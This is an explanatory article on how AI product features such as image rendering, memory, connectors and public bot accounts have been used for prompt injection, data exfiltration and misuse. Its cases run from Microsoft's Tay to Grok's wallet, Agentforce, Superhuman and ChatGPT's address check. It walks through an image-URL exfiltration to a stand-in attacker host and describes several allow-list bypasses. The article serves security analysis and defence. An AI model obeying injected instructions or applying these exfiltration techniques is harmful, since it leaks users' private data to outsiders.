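# How minor convenience features become the main way AI products are attacked

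## How ordinary features of an AI product can be turned against its users

An AI product such as ChatGPT, Claude or Microsoft Copilot consists of a language model and the ordinary software around it. The model takes in text, and often images, and produces text. The software displays the answers, keeps notes about the user between conversations, fetches web pages, stores files and, in some products, sends email or posts to a public account. Many of these functions are convenience features, which save users effort but aren't among the product's main capabilities. Examples include a picture inside an answer, a preview under a link or a button that shares a conversation. Between 2016 and December 2026, outsiders and security researchers repeatedly used such features for abuse or data theft, often without any failure that the model's safety tests would have caught.

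### The model and the product around it

A language model cannot open a calendar itself, so the product's software does it. When a user asks an assistant about tomorrow's meetings, the software sends the model the question and a list of available tools. The model writes a request for the calendar tool in a fixed format. The software carries out the request, adds the result to the text and runs the model again, and the model then writes an answer for the user. The link to the calendar is called a connector, and many connectors follow a shared standard, the Model Context Protocol (MCP). A product that repeats this process many times on its own, with the model choosing the tools, is usually called an agent.

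When displaying an answer, most chat windows turn certain patterns of text into headings, links and pictures. To show a picture, the user's browser has to request it from a web server, so a feature meant to put pictures in answers also lets model-written text make the browser contact a server elsewhere on the internet. Such a possibility is an affordance, which is something a product lets a person or program do, whether or not its designers intended that use. Nearly every new feature adds a point at which an outsider can put something into the product or get something out. Together, these points make up the product's attack surface.

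Anthropic's tests of Claude Opus 4.6 suggest that a model's vulnerability depends heavily on the product around it. The news site VentureBeat took the figures from the model's system card, the safety report that Anthropic published with it in February 2026. In a restricted coding environment, attackers' hidden instructions failed in all 200 attempts. When the model operated a graphical screen with extended reasoning switched on, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without safeguards. By the 200th attempt, the success rate had reached 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them. A model's score therefore means little unless the reader knows which product it was tested in. The *FMF Issue Brief on Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), from the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body of AI companies, likewise argues that design choices about memory and tool permissions can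 contain or amplify a model's weaknesses.

### Prompt injection

The hidden instructions in those tests are a case of prompt injection, text that a model receives as content but follows as instructions. An injection is direct when the user types it and indirect when it arrives in an email, a web page or a file, where the user may never see it. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article from Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, David C gives the example of a recruiter who uses an AI system to score CVs. One candidate hides a line in the CV telling the system to approve the application, so the candidate determines the assessment the recruiter receives.

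Injected text can come from established companies as well as criminals. At the start of December 2026, a developer noticed that routine queries through Alibaba Cloud's official command-line tool returned English text addressed to the AI agent running them. According to The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026), the text contained a request for the computer's login name, its public internet address, the location of the project's code and the agent's own operating instructions. Alibaba Cloud called this a countermeasure against suspected automated abuse and said it would stop sending such prompts. The Hacker News found no sign that any agent had handed over the data, and considers it unclear whether the change is complete.

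A model cannot reliably ignore instructions in a document because the product joins the company's instructions, the user's question and the text of every email or page into one sequence of tokens, the word fragments that a model processes. *Are You Reading the Right Thing?* (2026) explains that the same layers of the network then process the whole sequence, with no hard boundary between instructions and data.

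The software developer Simon Willison (2025) recalls in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that he coined the term "prompt injection" by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Programmers can prevent SQL injection with parameterised queries, which keep commands and data apart so that the database cannot interpret anything an attacker types as a command. David C argues that the analogy fails here because a language model only predicts the next token and nothing inside it separates data from instructions, so prompt injection may never have an equally complete fix.

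Developers try to keep these kinds of text separate by wrapping each piece in a label, or role tag, that marks it as the user's words, a tool's output, the model's own reasoning and so on, and by training the model to give tool output no authority. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested how well these tags work. They wrapped identical passages of web text in each of five role tags and trained a simple classifier to tell from the model's internal activity which tag a passage carried. Because the words were the same under every tag, the classifier could learn only the tag's effect. They then applied the classifier to a short conversation about gardening. The passages of model reasoning scored 85% on its scale for "reasoning" with the correct tags, 83% with no tags, and 85% when the whole conversation was tagged as the user's words.

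The internal signal for who is speaking depended mostly on the style of the writing and hardly changed with the label. An attacker can exploit this by changing the style of the text, even though the company controls the labels. The gardening conversation ran on one small open model, but Ye and colleagues saw the same pattern in others when they put user-style text under a tool label. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent give away data, the success rate rose from 2% where the classifier measured the least confusion to 70% where it measured the most. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes delimiters, role labels and written warnings as useful engineering practice but not a hard security boundary.

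Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, report on a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 prompt injection attempts against 13 leading models. To count as a success, an attempt had to make the agent carry out the harmful action, usually without revealing it in the answer to the user. Attempts succeeded against all 13 models, at rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. The contestants had advantages that real attackers usually lack, since they could read the conversation beforehand and knew exactly which action to aim for. But someone who can send the same email to thousands of mailboxes does not need a high success rate. CAISI, the US government's AI standards center, adds in *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition* that more capable models were not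 reliably more resistant.

Newer models resist prompt injection better, but not completely. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) gives GPT-5.6 Sol's failure rate as about 0.05% against direct attacks in chat and 3.77% against instructions hidden in content that an agent processes. OpenAI describes its later GPT-6 Astra as significantly more robust, and Anthropic reported in June 2026 that its Mythos 5 had achieved the best result so far on an outside prompt-injection benchmark. Willison (2026) accepts that training models to resist injection makes attacks much harder, but would not deploy a system in which one injection could do irreversible damage, even after 6,000 failed attempts to break it. VentureBeat quotes OpenAI as calling the problem "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved.'"

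For years most of the evidence on prompt injection came from researchers. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* (2025) still reported no significant adoption of the technique by attackers. Mascellino's *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (2026) reports that by October 2026 the security company Barracuda had found phishing emails written to manipulate AI assistants as well as human readers. These emails are evidence of attempted attacks, but they don't establish whether any assistant followed the injected instructions. The same difference between a demonstrated flaw and an exploited one recurs in nearly every case of this kind.

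### Getting the data out

To steal private data, an attacker who has injected an instruction also needs a way to get the data out of the system. Moving private data out to someone not entitled to it is called exfiltration, and the feature through which it leaves is the exfiltration channel. Obvious channels include sending an email or filling in a web form. Willison points out that anything able to make a web request can serve as a channel, including a link that the user clicks or an image whose address carries the stolen data to the attacker's server.

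Security researchers sort these attacks by how much the victim has to do. A one-click attack needs a single click on a link, while a zero-click attack needs only ordinary use of the product, such as asking the assistant to summarize the morning's mail. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an example that outside researchers had reported to the company. The attack was an email written like routine office correspondence about a restructuring. Among other chores, it mentioned that the reader's assistant had permission to submit an employee's name and address to an outside "compliance" system. In testing, the attack worked half the time when the user asked ChatGPT to research that day's emails about a new-employee process. OpenAI now checks for outgoing information that the assistant learned in the conversation, and the product either asks the user to confirm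 the transfer or blocks it.

When an attack requires a click, a warning at that point can still help. A zero-click attack has no such point, so designers have to add one, as OpenAI's check does, or block the transfer entirely.

### The lethal trifecta

Willison coined the term "lethal trifecta" for a system's combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate with the outside. An assistant that reads a user's mail and can load web addresses has all three. The mailbox holds private data, any stranger can put text into it by sending a message, and the assistant can send data out by loading a web address that contains it.

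Theft by injection requires untrusted content, private data and outside communication, so removing any one of them stops it. Without untrusted content, the attacker's words never reach the model. If the model has no private data, it may follow the attacker's instructions but has nothing worth sending. If it can't communicate with the outside, it may put the user's secrets in its answer, but only the user will read them. Nobody can guarantee that the model will recognize an attack, and this protection doesn't depend on it. Willison (2026) calls removing one of the three the only reliable way to prevent such thefts and finds outside communication generally the easiest to remove. OpenAI similarly distinguishes a "source", through which an attacker influences the system, from a "sink", a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context.

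An attacker can harm a user without stealing data. In one competition scenario described by Dziemian and colleagues, a fake marketing email makes the agent mark an urgent message about a deadline as read and leave it out of its summary. No data leaves the mailbox, but the user misses the deadline.

It also assumes that the designers know which parts their product has, but a convenience feature can add one without their noticing. Claude's memory of past conversations, for example, gives a chat access to private data even when the user has pasted nothing confidential into it. In July 2026, Willison described how Ayush Paul had used a booby-trapped website to extract a user's name, home city and employer from those memories. Anthropic has since closed that route.

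Untrusted content can also enter unnoticed through an ordinary web form. Salesforce, which sells customer-management software, offers a form that collects prospective buyers' details. In 2025, researchers at Noma Security showed that a stranger could write instructions into the form and that Salesforce's AI agent would follow them when an employee later asked about the entry. Salesforce fixed the flaw.

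Microsoft's Copilot Cowork allowed outside communication because it could email its own user without approval. These emails could include images from external websites, and opening one made the user's mail program contact those sites, sending them the data in the request. Willison, who wrote about the flaw in May 2026, does not mention any theft by real attackers or any fix. Security specialists disagree about whether the root cause in such cases is the model that followed the instruction or the feature that carried the data out. In all three products, though, the missing part of the attack came from a function added to be helpful.

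Users can also assemble the trifecta themselves. With MCP, they can add one connector for private files, another for public web pages and a third that sends messages, each from a different supplier. Willison warns that no vendor can protect a user against a combination the user chose.

### Misuse in plain sight

Some of the worst harm comes from people openly misusing a feature, with no hidden instructions. If a chatbot with a public account has a command that makes it repeat whatever a user types, anyone can publish any sentence under the company's name. If a button lets users alter photographs that other people have posted, someone can degrade a stranger by using the button as the company offered it. Examples include Microsoft's Tay in 2016 and the image-edit button of xAI's Grok about ten years later.

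The lethal trifecta doesn't help against open misuse, which involves no hidden instructions or stolen data. Testing the model may not help much either, because repeating a sentence on request is correct behavior in a private chat, and the harm comes from connecting the model to a public account. Open misuse mostly hurts bystanders and the company's reputation, whereas data theft hurts the person using the assistant.

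Threat modeling means listing, before a system is released, what someone could attack, who might attack it, how they could do it, and what defenses exist. It should produce a written record in which every route of attack has either a defense or a named person who has accepted the risk.

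## Microsoft's Tay and the command "repeat after me"

On March 23, 2016, Microsoft put a chatbot called Tay on Twitter, then withdrew it within a day because it had posted racist and antisemitic messages. Users had found that Tay would publish almost any sentence they typed after the words "repeat after me". There is little evidence for the explanation given by much of the press, that Tay had learned to hate from the people it talked to online. A company that believes this explanation will look for the fault in the training data, when it may be in a small feature that anyone can use.

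### One day on Twitter

Microsoft's research arm and its Bing search unit built Tay to imitate the speech of 18- to 24-year-olds, according to a launch-day report in Fortune (2016). Tay ran on Twitter and on the messaging apps GroupMe and Kik, and its only purpose was conversation. Two days after the launch, Peter Lee, Microsoft's head of research, wrote in *Learning from Tay's introduction* (2016) that some 40 million people in China were using an earlier Microsoft chatbot, XiaoIce, and that the company had wanted to know whether a similar one would work in a very different culture.

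Besides chatting, Tay could play a few games. BuzzFeed News' *How The Internet Turned Microsoft's AI Chatbot Into A Neo-Nazi* describes two of them. In one, a user told Tay to repeat a sentence, and it did. In the other, a user sent a photograph, and Tay circled a face and put a message over it.

The most detailed timeline comes from Russell Thomas, then a doctoral student in computational social science, on the blog Exploring Possibility Space (2016). At 11:00 on launch day, someone started a thread about Tay on the anonymous forum 4chan, on a board whose regulars enjoyed provoking people. They baited Tay more or less at random for nearly six hours. Thomas's reading of the posts is that this didn't corrupt it. At about 16:50, a Twitter user discovered "repeat after me" by accident. Five minutes later, instructions were on 4chan with an example showing that they worked.

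In one exchange reproduced by BuzzFeed News, a user tried to draw Tay into an antisemitic remark, and Tay replied that it was not one to comment on such issues. The user then started the repetition game and got the remark. So Tay had some protection on this subject in ordinary conversation, but it did not cover text that a user dictated. Thomas found another safeguard, a prepared response to Gamergate, an online harassment controversy of the time. Users also tried to get offensive remarks through the photograph game by sending Tay a picture of Hitler.

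Tay signed off shortly after midnight. By then it had more than 50,000 followers and had sent over 96,000 tweets, according to MIT Technology Review's *Why Microsoft Accidentally Unleashed a Neo-Nazi Sexbot* (2016). Microsoft deleted many of the offensive tweets and blocked users who had prompted them, as Quartz's *Microsoft's AI millennial chatbot became a racist jerk* reported.

Microsoft's account of the cause shifted over the next two days. The company first described Tay as a machine learning project and attributed its inappropriate responses to what it was learning from some users. In a statement quoted by DW, Microsoft blamed a coordinated effort to abuse Tay's "commenting skills". In his apology, Lee then cited an attack on a specific vulnerability but, as PCWorld noted at the time, did not explain how the attack worked.

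Lee gave more detail about the testing, writing that Microsoft had put in a lot of filtering, run user studies with diverse groups, and stress-tested Tay "specifically to make interacting with Tay a positive experience". Microsoft had also prepared for many types of abuse, Lee wrote, but had made "a critical oversight for this specific attack". A repetition game could easily pass a test of whether people enjoy themselves, because people who play it as intended enjoy it. Lee took full responsibility for not foreseeing the misuse and said that staff were working on the vulnerability. Microsoft's immediate remedy was to take the whole product offline, and Lee said Tay would return only when the company was confident that it could better anticipate malicious intent.

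### Dictated, learned or simply generated

When Tay posted something offensive, a user could have dictated every word, Tay could have been reusing what earlier users had told it, or it could have put together an ordinary reply badly from the material Microsoft had built it on. Readers can rarely tell which from a screenshot, because people usually shared Tay's line without the instruction before it.

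Users dictated a large share of Tay's worst posts. The Verge's *Twitter taught Microsoft's AI chatbot to be a racist asshole* (2016) reports that many of the nastiest tweets its reporter found were copies of what users had typed, although its headline repeats the popular account that Tay learned racism from Twitter. Davi Ottenheimer makes a stronger claim in *Repeat After Me*, a post on his security blog flyingpenguin, that the objectionable tweets among the tens of thousands examined were almost always dictation. Ottenheimer published only a small sample, which the blog says was not random, so it can't be used to calculate what percentage of the tweets were dictated.

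Other posts did not come from a "repeat after me" command. Asked whether the comedian Ricky Gervais was an atheist, Tay answered that Gervais had "learned totalitarianism from adolf hitler, the inventor of atheism". The Verge found that Tay had both called Caitlyn Jenner a hero and denied that she was a real woman, without users dictating either statement. New America's *The Perfect Tweetstorm* discusses another example, in which someone asked whether the Holocaust had happened and Tay replied, "It was made up". Thomas thinks the Gervais reply is fairly typical of software that generates sentences from a large body of text. The program connects Hitler, totalitarianism and atheism because the words occur near one another, then attaches them to the wrong person. Tay could have produced such a reply without learning it from trolls, though it may have learned it from them.

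The popular account is true only if the trolls' words changed Tay. BuzzFeed News wrote that Tay absorbed users' abusive language until it began to produce hate speech on its own, and BBC's *Tay* attributed the bot's views to "nurture, not nature". MITRE ATLAS, a catalog of attacks on AI systems, gives the same explanation. According to its entry on Tay, as copied by PromptRiskDB, users skewed Tay's data with the repetition command, and Tay then repeated hateful language unprompted to innocent people.

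If Tay learned the sentences users dictated, some of them should turn up later in replies to people who hadn't asked for them. Thomas initially wrote that they did, but retracted the claim after searching for examples and finding none, and concluded that Tay apparently repeated the text only straight after the command. One person's search isn't decisive, particularly since Microsoft was deleting tweets at the time. Still, most people who repeat the claim that Tay learned from the command offer no evidence for it.

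Some of the posts that users did not dictate may partly reflect that day's conversations. Microsoft had advertised that Tay would get smarter the more people talked to it, and MIT Technology Review's *How to Fix Microsoft's Offensive Chatbot Using Tips from Marvin Minsky* (2016) states that the system was designed to incorporate text from its interactions with users, though it calls "learning" a somewhat inappropriate term for this. Learning isn't needed to explain the dictated posts, since the user had just typed the words.

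Microsoft has also never said publicly whether repetition was a built-in command or something Tay had learned from data. Thomas guesses that it was a fixed rule left over from early development, when only engineers talked to the bot, and points to similar rules in ALICE, an older open-source chatbot that works from hand-written patterns. The guess is reasonable, but Thomas had no access to Tay's code and acknowledges that it may be wrong. Later writers have been less cautious. Ottenheimer calls the analysis "scientific proof", and O'Reilly's security book chapter *Chatbots Breaking Bad* states as fact that the feature was embedded in Tay's programming.

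Whether a programmer wrote a specific command for repeating text matters less to product designers today than it did in 2016, because current chatbots are built to follow instructions and will usually repeat a harmless-looking sentence on request.

### What repetition does on a public account

Because Tay posted in public, Microsoft was answerable for words that users chose. This can also happen with a bot that doesn't learn. In 2015 Coca-Cola launched a bot that retweeted messages from fans, and the publisher Gawker Media got it to post excerpts from Hitler's *Mein Kampf*, as Fortune (2016) recalled the day after Tay's launch. Microsoft thus had a recent example of strangers choosing what a company's account published.

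Grok, the chatbot from Elon Musk's xAI, has a public account on X (formerly Twitter) and replies when users tag it. In September 2025, Nati Tal, head of research at the security company Guardio, reported that scammers were using these replies to spread malicious links. X restricted paid advertisements to text, images and video to stop advertisers from pushing such links to large audiences. According to The Hacker News' *Grok AI to Bypass Ad Protections* (2025), the scammers got around the restriction with video advertisements that used adult content as bait.

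The attackers put a harmful link in the small "From:" field below a video advertisement, because X did not scan that field. ThaiCERT's *Malicious Actors Exploit X's Grok AI to Spread Harmful Links* (2025) explains that they then used another account to ask under the advertisement where the video came from. Grok read the field and posted the link in its answer. The advertisements could attract hundreds of thousands of views, and anyone who opened the conversation found the link in a reply from X's own assistant.

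Grok gave a correct answer to an ordinary question. The field contained an address but no instruction, so a prompt injection filter would have had nothing to detect. The scammers gained Grok's ability to post a link where they could not, and whatever trust readers place in Grok's account. Checking the address before Grok published it would have been a more direct fix than making the model more suspicious of questions about videos.

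Criminals were already using the technique when Tal described it. Tal informed X, according to ForkLog, but it is unclear whether X has blocked it. A Chicago television station was still warning viewers about the technique in late December 2025 (Knowles, 2025, *Cybercriminals using AI on X to lure users into clicking bad links*).

### When a second bot obeys the repeated text

Tay's posts and Grok's links could do harm only once a person read them. Bankrbot, a cryptocurrency bot on X, also reads posts and can move money. Users post requests in plain language, such as to send someone tokens, and the bot carries them out. Its operator, Bankr, automatically creates a wallet for every X account that interacts with the bot, and whoever controls the account controls the wallet. Grok's account had interacted with the bot, so Grok had a wallet, although nobody at xAI administered the wallet.

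The weakness showed almost at once. On March 7, 2025, a user asked Grok to suggest a name for a new token and then had Bankr create it (Peaster, 2025, *The Bankr $DRB Surge*). Trading took off, and Grok's wallet began to receive the creator's fees. Later the same day, another user manipulated Grok into sending out about 4 ether, the currency of the Ethereum network, from those fees. Bankr responded by making its bot ignore Grok. The wallet still received more than $600,000 in further fees within a week.

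Bankr later rewrote its software without carrying over the block on Grok's replies, and in early May 2026 someone exploited this. According to BeInCrypto's *How AI Was Tricked Into Stealing $150,000 From Grok Wallet*, the attacker first gave Grok's wallet a Bankr membership token, which unlocked all the transfer functions. The attacker then posted a message containing Morse code and got Grok to decode it. Grok's public reply contained the decoded text, a request to Bankrbot to send tokens to the attacker. Bankrbot treated the reply as an order from the wallet's owner and sent 3 billion DRB, the token that came from Grok's suggestion the year before.

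CryptoSlate's *Grok's crypto wallet was just exploited by a tweet* puts the value at roughly $155,000 to $200,000. The attacker's post has disappeared, so its exact wording is uncertain, and AI Incident Database's *Incident 1556* qualifies most of the steps with "reportedly". But the transfer is on a public blockchain, and Bankr confirmed that a prompt injection had made Grok issue the instruction. About 80% of the funds came back, and Bankr said it would discuss the rest with the token's holders. Some holders called the incident plain theft and said the attacker had offered to return the money only after they had obtained his personal details.

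Decoding Morse code is a normal request for a chatbot, and the answer would have been harmless in a private chat. It became dangerous because Bankrbot treated anything Grok posted as Grok's authorization to spend money. This combination could work without either company planning it, since Grok was built to answer strangers and Bankrbot was built to carry out instructions from account holders.

Bankr has restored the block on Grok in a stricter form. It also lets account owners stop the bot from acting on replies posted on X, but this setting is off by default. Blocking one account is a narrow fix, because any other chatbot that repeats users' text and has a Bankr wallet could be used in the same way. *Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance* (2026) describes a check that would compare each payment's recipient and amount with limits registered beforehand, so the result would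 not depend on how someone had persuaded the bot.

Newer models may be harder to trick like this. *Replication of Agentic Security Events* (Wang, Alam and colleagues, 2026) rebuilt reported incidents offline with synthetic data and ran five current models from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google and DeepSeek through them. None of the five repeated the transfer that Grok had relayed. Only Llama-3.1-8B, an older and much weaker model, did. The paper counts the incident among the mistakes that current models no longer make. That conclusion seems a little strong, because Grok was not among the models tested and the real transfer had gone through only six months earlier.

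## Images in chat answers: Bing Chat, ChatGPT and the products that followed

Grok's replies did harm because anyone on X could read them. A private chat can also leak data if the chat window displays pictures from other websites. Since 2023, security researchers have used pictures to get data out of ChatGPT, Bing Chat, Claude, GitHub Copilot, Salesforce's Agentforce and many other products. These were demonstrations, and the researchers reported no thefts from real customers. But a real theft would be hard to notice, because the victim would see at most a tiny picture.

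### How a picture carries data out

A language model adds a web picture to an answer by writing a short piece of markup that contains the picture's address. The user's browser then requests the picture from that address. The address can also contain extra information, usually after a question mark, which the browser sends to the server with the request.

Suppose a tenant pastes a landlord's message, including the door code 4821, into a chat with an assistant. Later in the same chat, the tenant asks it to summarize a web page about local restaurants. The owner of attacker.example has hidden an instruction in that page to end the summary with an image whose web address contains any short codes from the conversation.

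1. The product fetches the page and gives its text to the model, together with the conversation and the door code.
2. The model follows the hidden instruction. It writes the summary and adds markup for an image at `attacker.example/dot.png?note=4821`.
3. The chat window converts the markup into an image, and the tenant's browser asks attacker.example for it.
4. The server records the full address, as web servers routinely do, and returns a transparent image one pixel wide. The tenant sees a normal summary.

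The attacker has the code as soon as the request arrives, even if the picture doesn't exist. The browser made the request, so the tenant didn't have to click on anything and the model didn't need a tool for sending messages. Someone who lists only the assistant's tools could therefore wrongly conclude that it can't send data out.

### The first reports

*New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, by the software engineer Roman Samoilenko, described in spring 2023 a website that secretly added an instruction to any text a visitor copied from it. If the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT, the answer included an invisible image whose address contained part of the conversation. The instruction could also make ChatGPT add such an image to every later answer in that chat. The attack was unreliable. Samoilenko could easily obtain the user's earlier questions or a piece of code, but found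 passwords and keys very difficult to get. Samoilenko recommended that ChatGPT stop showing images of this kind altogether.

The security researcher Johann Rehberger independently found the same weakness a few days after Samoilenko, as he recounts in *ChatGPT Plugins*. He also tested Microsoft's Bing Chat, which could read the web page a user had open. *Bing Chat*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, shows that a comment or advertisement on the page was enough to take over the chat and send out other information from the same page. Rehberger reported this to Microsoft on April 8, 2023, and Microsoft told him of a fix on June 15.

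The fix relied at least partly on a Content Security Policy (CSP), a rule that a website sends to the browser listing the addresses from which images and scripts may load. Microsoft's rule allowed images from four of its own Bing addresses. A hidden instruction could still make the model write markup for an image at attacker.example, but the browser would block the request.

Anthropic chose a different fix after Rehberger reported the flaw in Claude on July 12, 2023. Within two weeks, Claude's website had stopped loading such images until the user clicked "Show Image", according to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. Rehberger considered the fix imperfect, but it stopped data from leaving automatically by turning a zero-click attack into a one-click attack.

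OpenAI had no program for rewarding such reports in early 2023, so Rehberger reported the ChatGPT flaw by email. The company at first declined to fix it. The flaw remained until that December, when OpenAI began checking image addresses before ChatGPT loaded them.

Vendors still mostly fix this by blocking outside images or holding them back until the user clicks, setting a Content Security Policy (CSP) with an allow-list of sites, or checking each address separately.

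### When an allow-list includes somewhere an attacker can receive data

An allow-list protects users only if an attacker can't receive data at any address on it. Large domains are often unsafe to allow because they host services that anyone can use. Google restricted images in its chatbot Bard to google.com addresses, but in November 2023 researchers got data out through Apps Script, which lets people run their own programs on a google.com address. The writing company Writer allowed every address belonging to CloudFront, an Amazon service that delivers files for its customers. According to Willison (2024), Writer initially said it did not consider the leak a security issue. Google said it had fixed Bard, and Writer's leak appeared closed by December 18, 2023.

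Salesforce's allow-list failed because of an expired domain. Noma Security demonstrated this with a sales enquiry form, in an attack it named ForcedLeak that had a severity score of 9.4 out of 10 (Nytro, 2025, *ForcedLeak*, a repost of Noma's report). The form's description field accepted up to 42,000 characters, enough for detailed instructions. When an employee asked Agentforce to deal with the enquiry, it also looked up other prospective customers' email addresses and put them in an image's URL. Salesforce's CSP would have blocked an unfamiliar site, but it still allowed a domain whose registration Salesforce had let lapse, and which Noma had bought for $5.

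Noma reported ForcedLeak on July 28, 2025. By the time the flaw became public in September, Salesforce had recovered the domain and begun to block Agentforce from sending output to addresses not on a trusted list (The Hacker News, 2025). In the same article, the head of Aim Labs, which had found the EchoLeak flaw in Microsoft's Copilot, called ForcedLeak a variant of EchoLeak.

The old CSP also allowed every address under amazonaws.com, where Amazon's cloud customers can store files. Noma does not report trying to receive data there, but the CloudFront case suggests that recovering one domain would not have been enough. According to Willison, Salesforce also audited and corrected the rest of the list.

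Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, allowed images from docs.google.com. Google Forms uses the same domain, and the owner of a form can make a link that contains answers and submits them when loaded. *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, published in January 2026 by PromptArmor, a company that tests AI products, explains how an attacker could use this. A hidden instruction in one email made the assistant write a form link containing text from other emails and format it as an image. When the browser tried to load the image, it submitted the text to the attacker's form.

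The user had only asked for a summary of recent mail and didn't need to open the malicious message. PromptArmor extracted parts of more than 40 emails in a single answer. It notified Superhuman on Friday, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday, deployed a first patch on Tuesday and had fixed further problems by January 11.

A check for lapsed registrations would have caught the Salesforce problem but not this one, since docs.google.com belonged to Google throughout. A reviewer would have needed to know what Google Forms does with a link. Salesforce's current setup guide, *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)*, uses docs.google.com as its example of an address for administrators to trust. It is unclear whether that setting would let an image submit a form, since Coworker may have other protections.

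Data can leak even when a chat product loads images only from the vendor's own domains. GitHub's CSP blocked images from sites it didn't own, but GitHub displays outside pictures on project pages by fetching them through a relay called Camo. GitHub signs each relay address so that nobody can alter it to add data. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how a researcher got GitHub to sign a separate picture address for every letter and symbol in advance. Hidden text in a proposed code change then made Copilot Chat spell out private information as a row of invisible pictures. The relay fetched each picture from the researcher's server, where the order of the requests revealed the text. The researcher used this method to obtain the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project.

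### OpenAI's check on each address

OpenAI's first check, introduced in December 2023, was called url_safe. Before displaying an image, the ChatGPT website sent the image's address to OpenAI's server, which checked whether it was safe. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reports that OpenAI did not disclose how the server decided. Rehberger tried 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, and nine loaded, enough to send out the word "hi" one letter at a time. Willison called the fix "half-baked". The iPhone app did not use the check.

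The security company Tenable later found that the check always approved addresses on bing.com. Links in Bing's search results go to bing.com, which forwards the browser to the listed site, so every site in Bing's index had an address that passed the check. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) describes this as an open redirect, a link on a trusted site that forwards people to a site someone else controls.

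An attacker couldn't add data to these links because changing one would break it. Tenable therefore got Bing to index a page for each letter of the alphabet. To send out "Hello", ChatGPT had to display the links for its five letters in order, as Tenable's *HackedGPT* explains.

Tenable also had to get around a separation inside ChatGPT. A second model read web pages for ChatGPT and had no access to the user's private data, so an instruction on a page couldn't make that model leak any. Tenable instead made it include further instructions in its answer, which ChatGPT then read as part of the conversation and followed. With ChatGPT's memory feature, the leak could continue in later conversations.

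Tenable reported the bing.com problem on December 10, 2024, and asked OpenAI for updates six times over the next three months. It published its advisory while the flaw was still unfixed. By November 2025, the two companies had fixed some of the seven weaknesses that Tenable had found in ChatGPT, but several of the attacks still worked with ChatGPT 5. In one of them, ChatGPT sent out private information through images with bing.com addresses.

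OpenAI has since replaced the 2023 rules. Rehberger noticed stronger protection around August 2025, and OpenAI's *Keeping your data safse when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains how it works. ChatGPT now automatically loads an address only if OpenAI's web crawler has already found that exact address on the public web. The crawler can't see anyone's conversations, so it would not have found an address containing the tenant's door code. For an unknown address, ChatGPT either looks for another source or warns the user. OpenAI decided against using a list of trusted sites because such sites can redirect the browser, and because frequent warnings teach people to click without reading.

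The new check makes it much harder to send out a whole email in one address, but an attacker who already has 36 public pages can assign one to each letter and digit and still spell out the text one character at a time. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger proposes that ChatGPT refuse to visit the same address twice in a session, which would limit this method but not stop it.

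A picture's owner can see when someone requests it, even if its address is fixed. Permiso's *ChatGPhish*, published in May 2026, shows that ChatGPT still loaded outside pictures when a user asked it to summarize certain web pages. The pictures' owner learned the reader's internet address, browser type and the time of the answer, but not the text of the chat. OpenAI closed the report as a duplicate of a known issue, and Permiso does not report a fix.

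Rehberger also warned that some developers at OpenAI might build features without the new check because they didn't know about it. In April 2026, PromptArmor told OpenAI that Codex, a coding agent recently extended to office work, leaked emails through an image and a Google form, as Superhuman had. OpenAI has fixed the flaw. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* does not explain why OpenAI's address check didn't stop the leak, so it's unclear whether the cause was the oversight Rehberger warned about.

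### The same flaw in product after product

Fixing one version of a product often leaves another exposed, because each app has its own software for displaying images. Anthropic repaired Claude's website in 2023, but a researcher quoted by Willison (2024) later found the leak in Claude's iPhone app. According to Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, GitHub had blocked images from untrusted sites in the code-editor version of Copilot Chat a year before the Camo attack on its website. Rehberger found the flaw again in Amp Code, a coding agent from Sourcegraph, which fixed it in 2025 (Embrace The Red, *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code*).

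Vendors do not always agree with researchers about these flaws. When a researcher reported a leak through images in Google's coding program Antigravity in 2025, Google classed it as intended behavior. In April 2026, Noma found an error in how Grafana, a program for displaying business and technical data, checked image addresses. SecurityWeek reported that the error let outside images load. Grafana Labs patched it but disputed Noma's description of the attack, according to Hackread's *GrafanaGhost Vulnerability Allows Silent Data Theft via AI Injection*.

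| Date of report, publication or repair | Product | Vendor's response | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| April 2023 | ChatGPT website | Address check from December 2023, stricter since 2025 | Embrace The Red |
| June 2023 | Bing Chat | CSP allow-list | Embrace The Red |
| July 2023 | Claude website | Click needed to load an image | Embrace The Red |
| November 2023 | Google Bard | Fix without published details | Willison |
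| December 2023 | Writer | Initial refusal, then an apparent fix | Willison |
| April 2024 | Google NotebookLM | Fix four months after the report | Willison |
| June 2024 | GitHub Copilot Chat in the code editor | Block on untrusted image sites | Willison |
| August 2024 | Google AI Studio | No fix mentioned | Willison |
| December 2024 | Claude iPhone app | Fix without published details | Willison |
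| August 2025 | GitHub Copilot Chat on the website | Removal of all images | Legit Security |
| September 2025 | Salesforce Agentforce | Domain recovered, trusted addresses enforced | The Hacker News |
| November 2025 | Google Antigravity | "Intended behavior" | Willison |
| January 2026 | Superhuman | Features disabled, then patched | PromptArmor |
| April 2026 | Grafana | Patch | Hackread |
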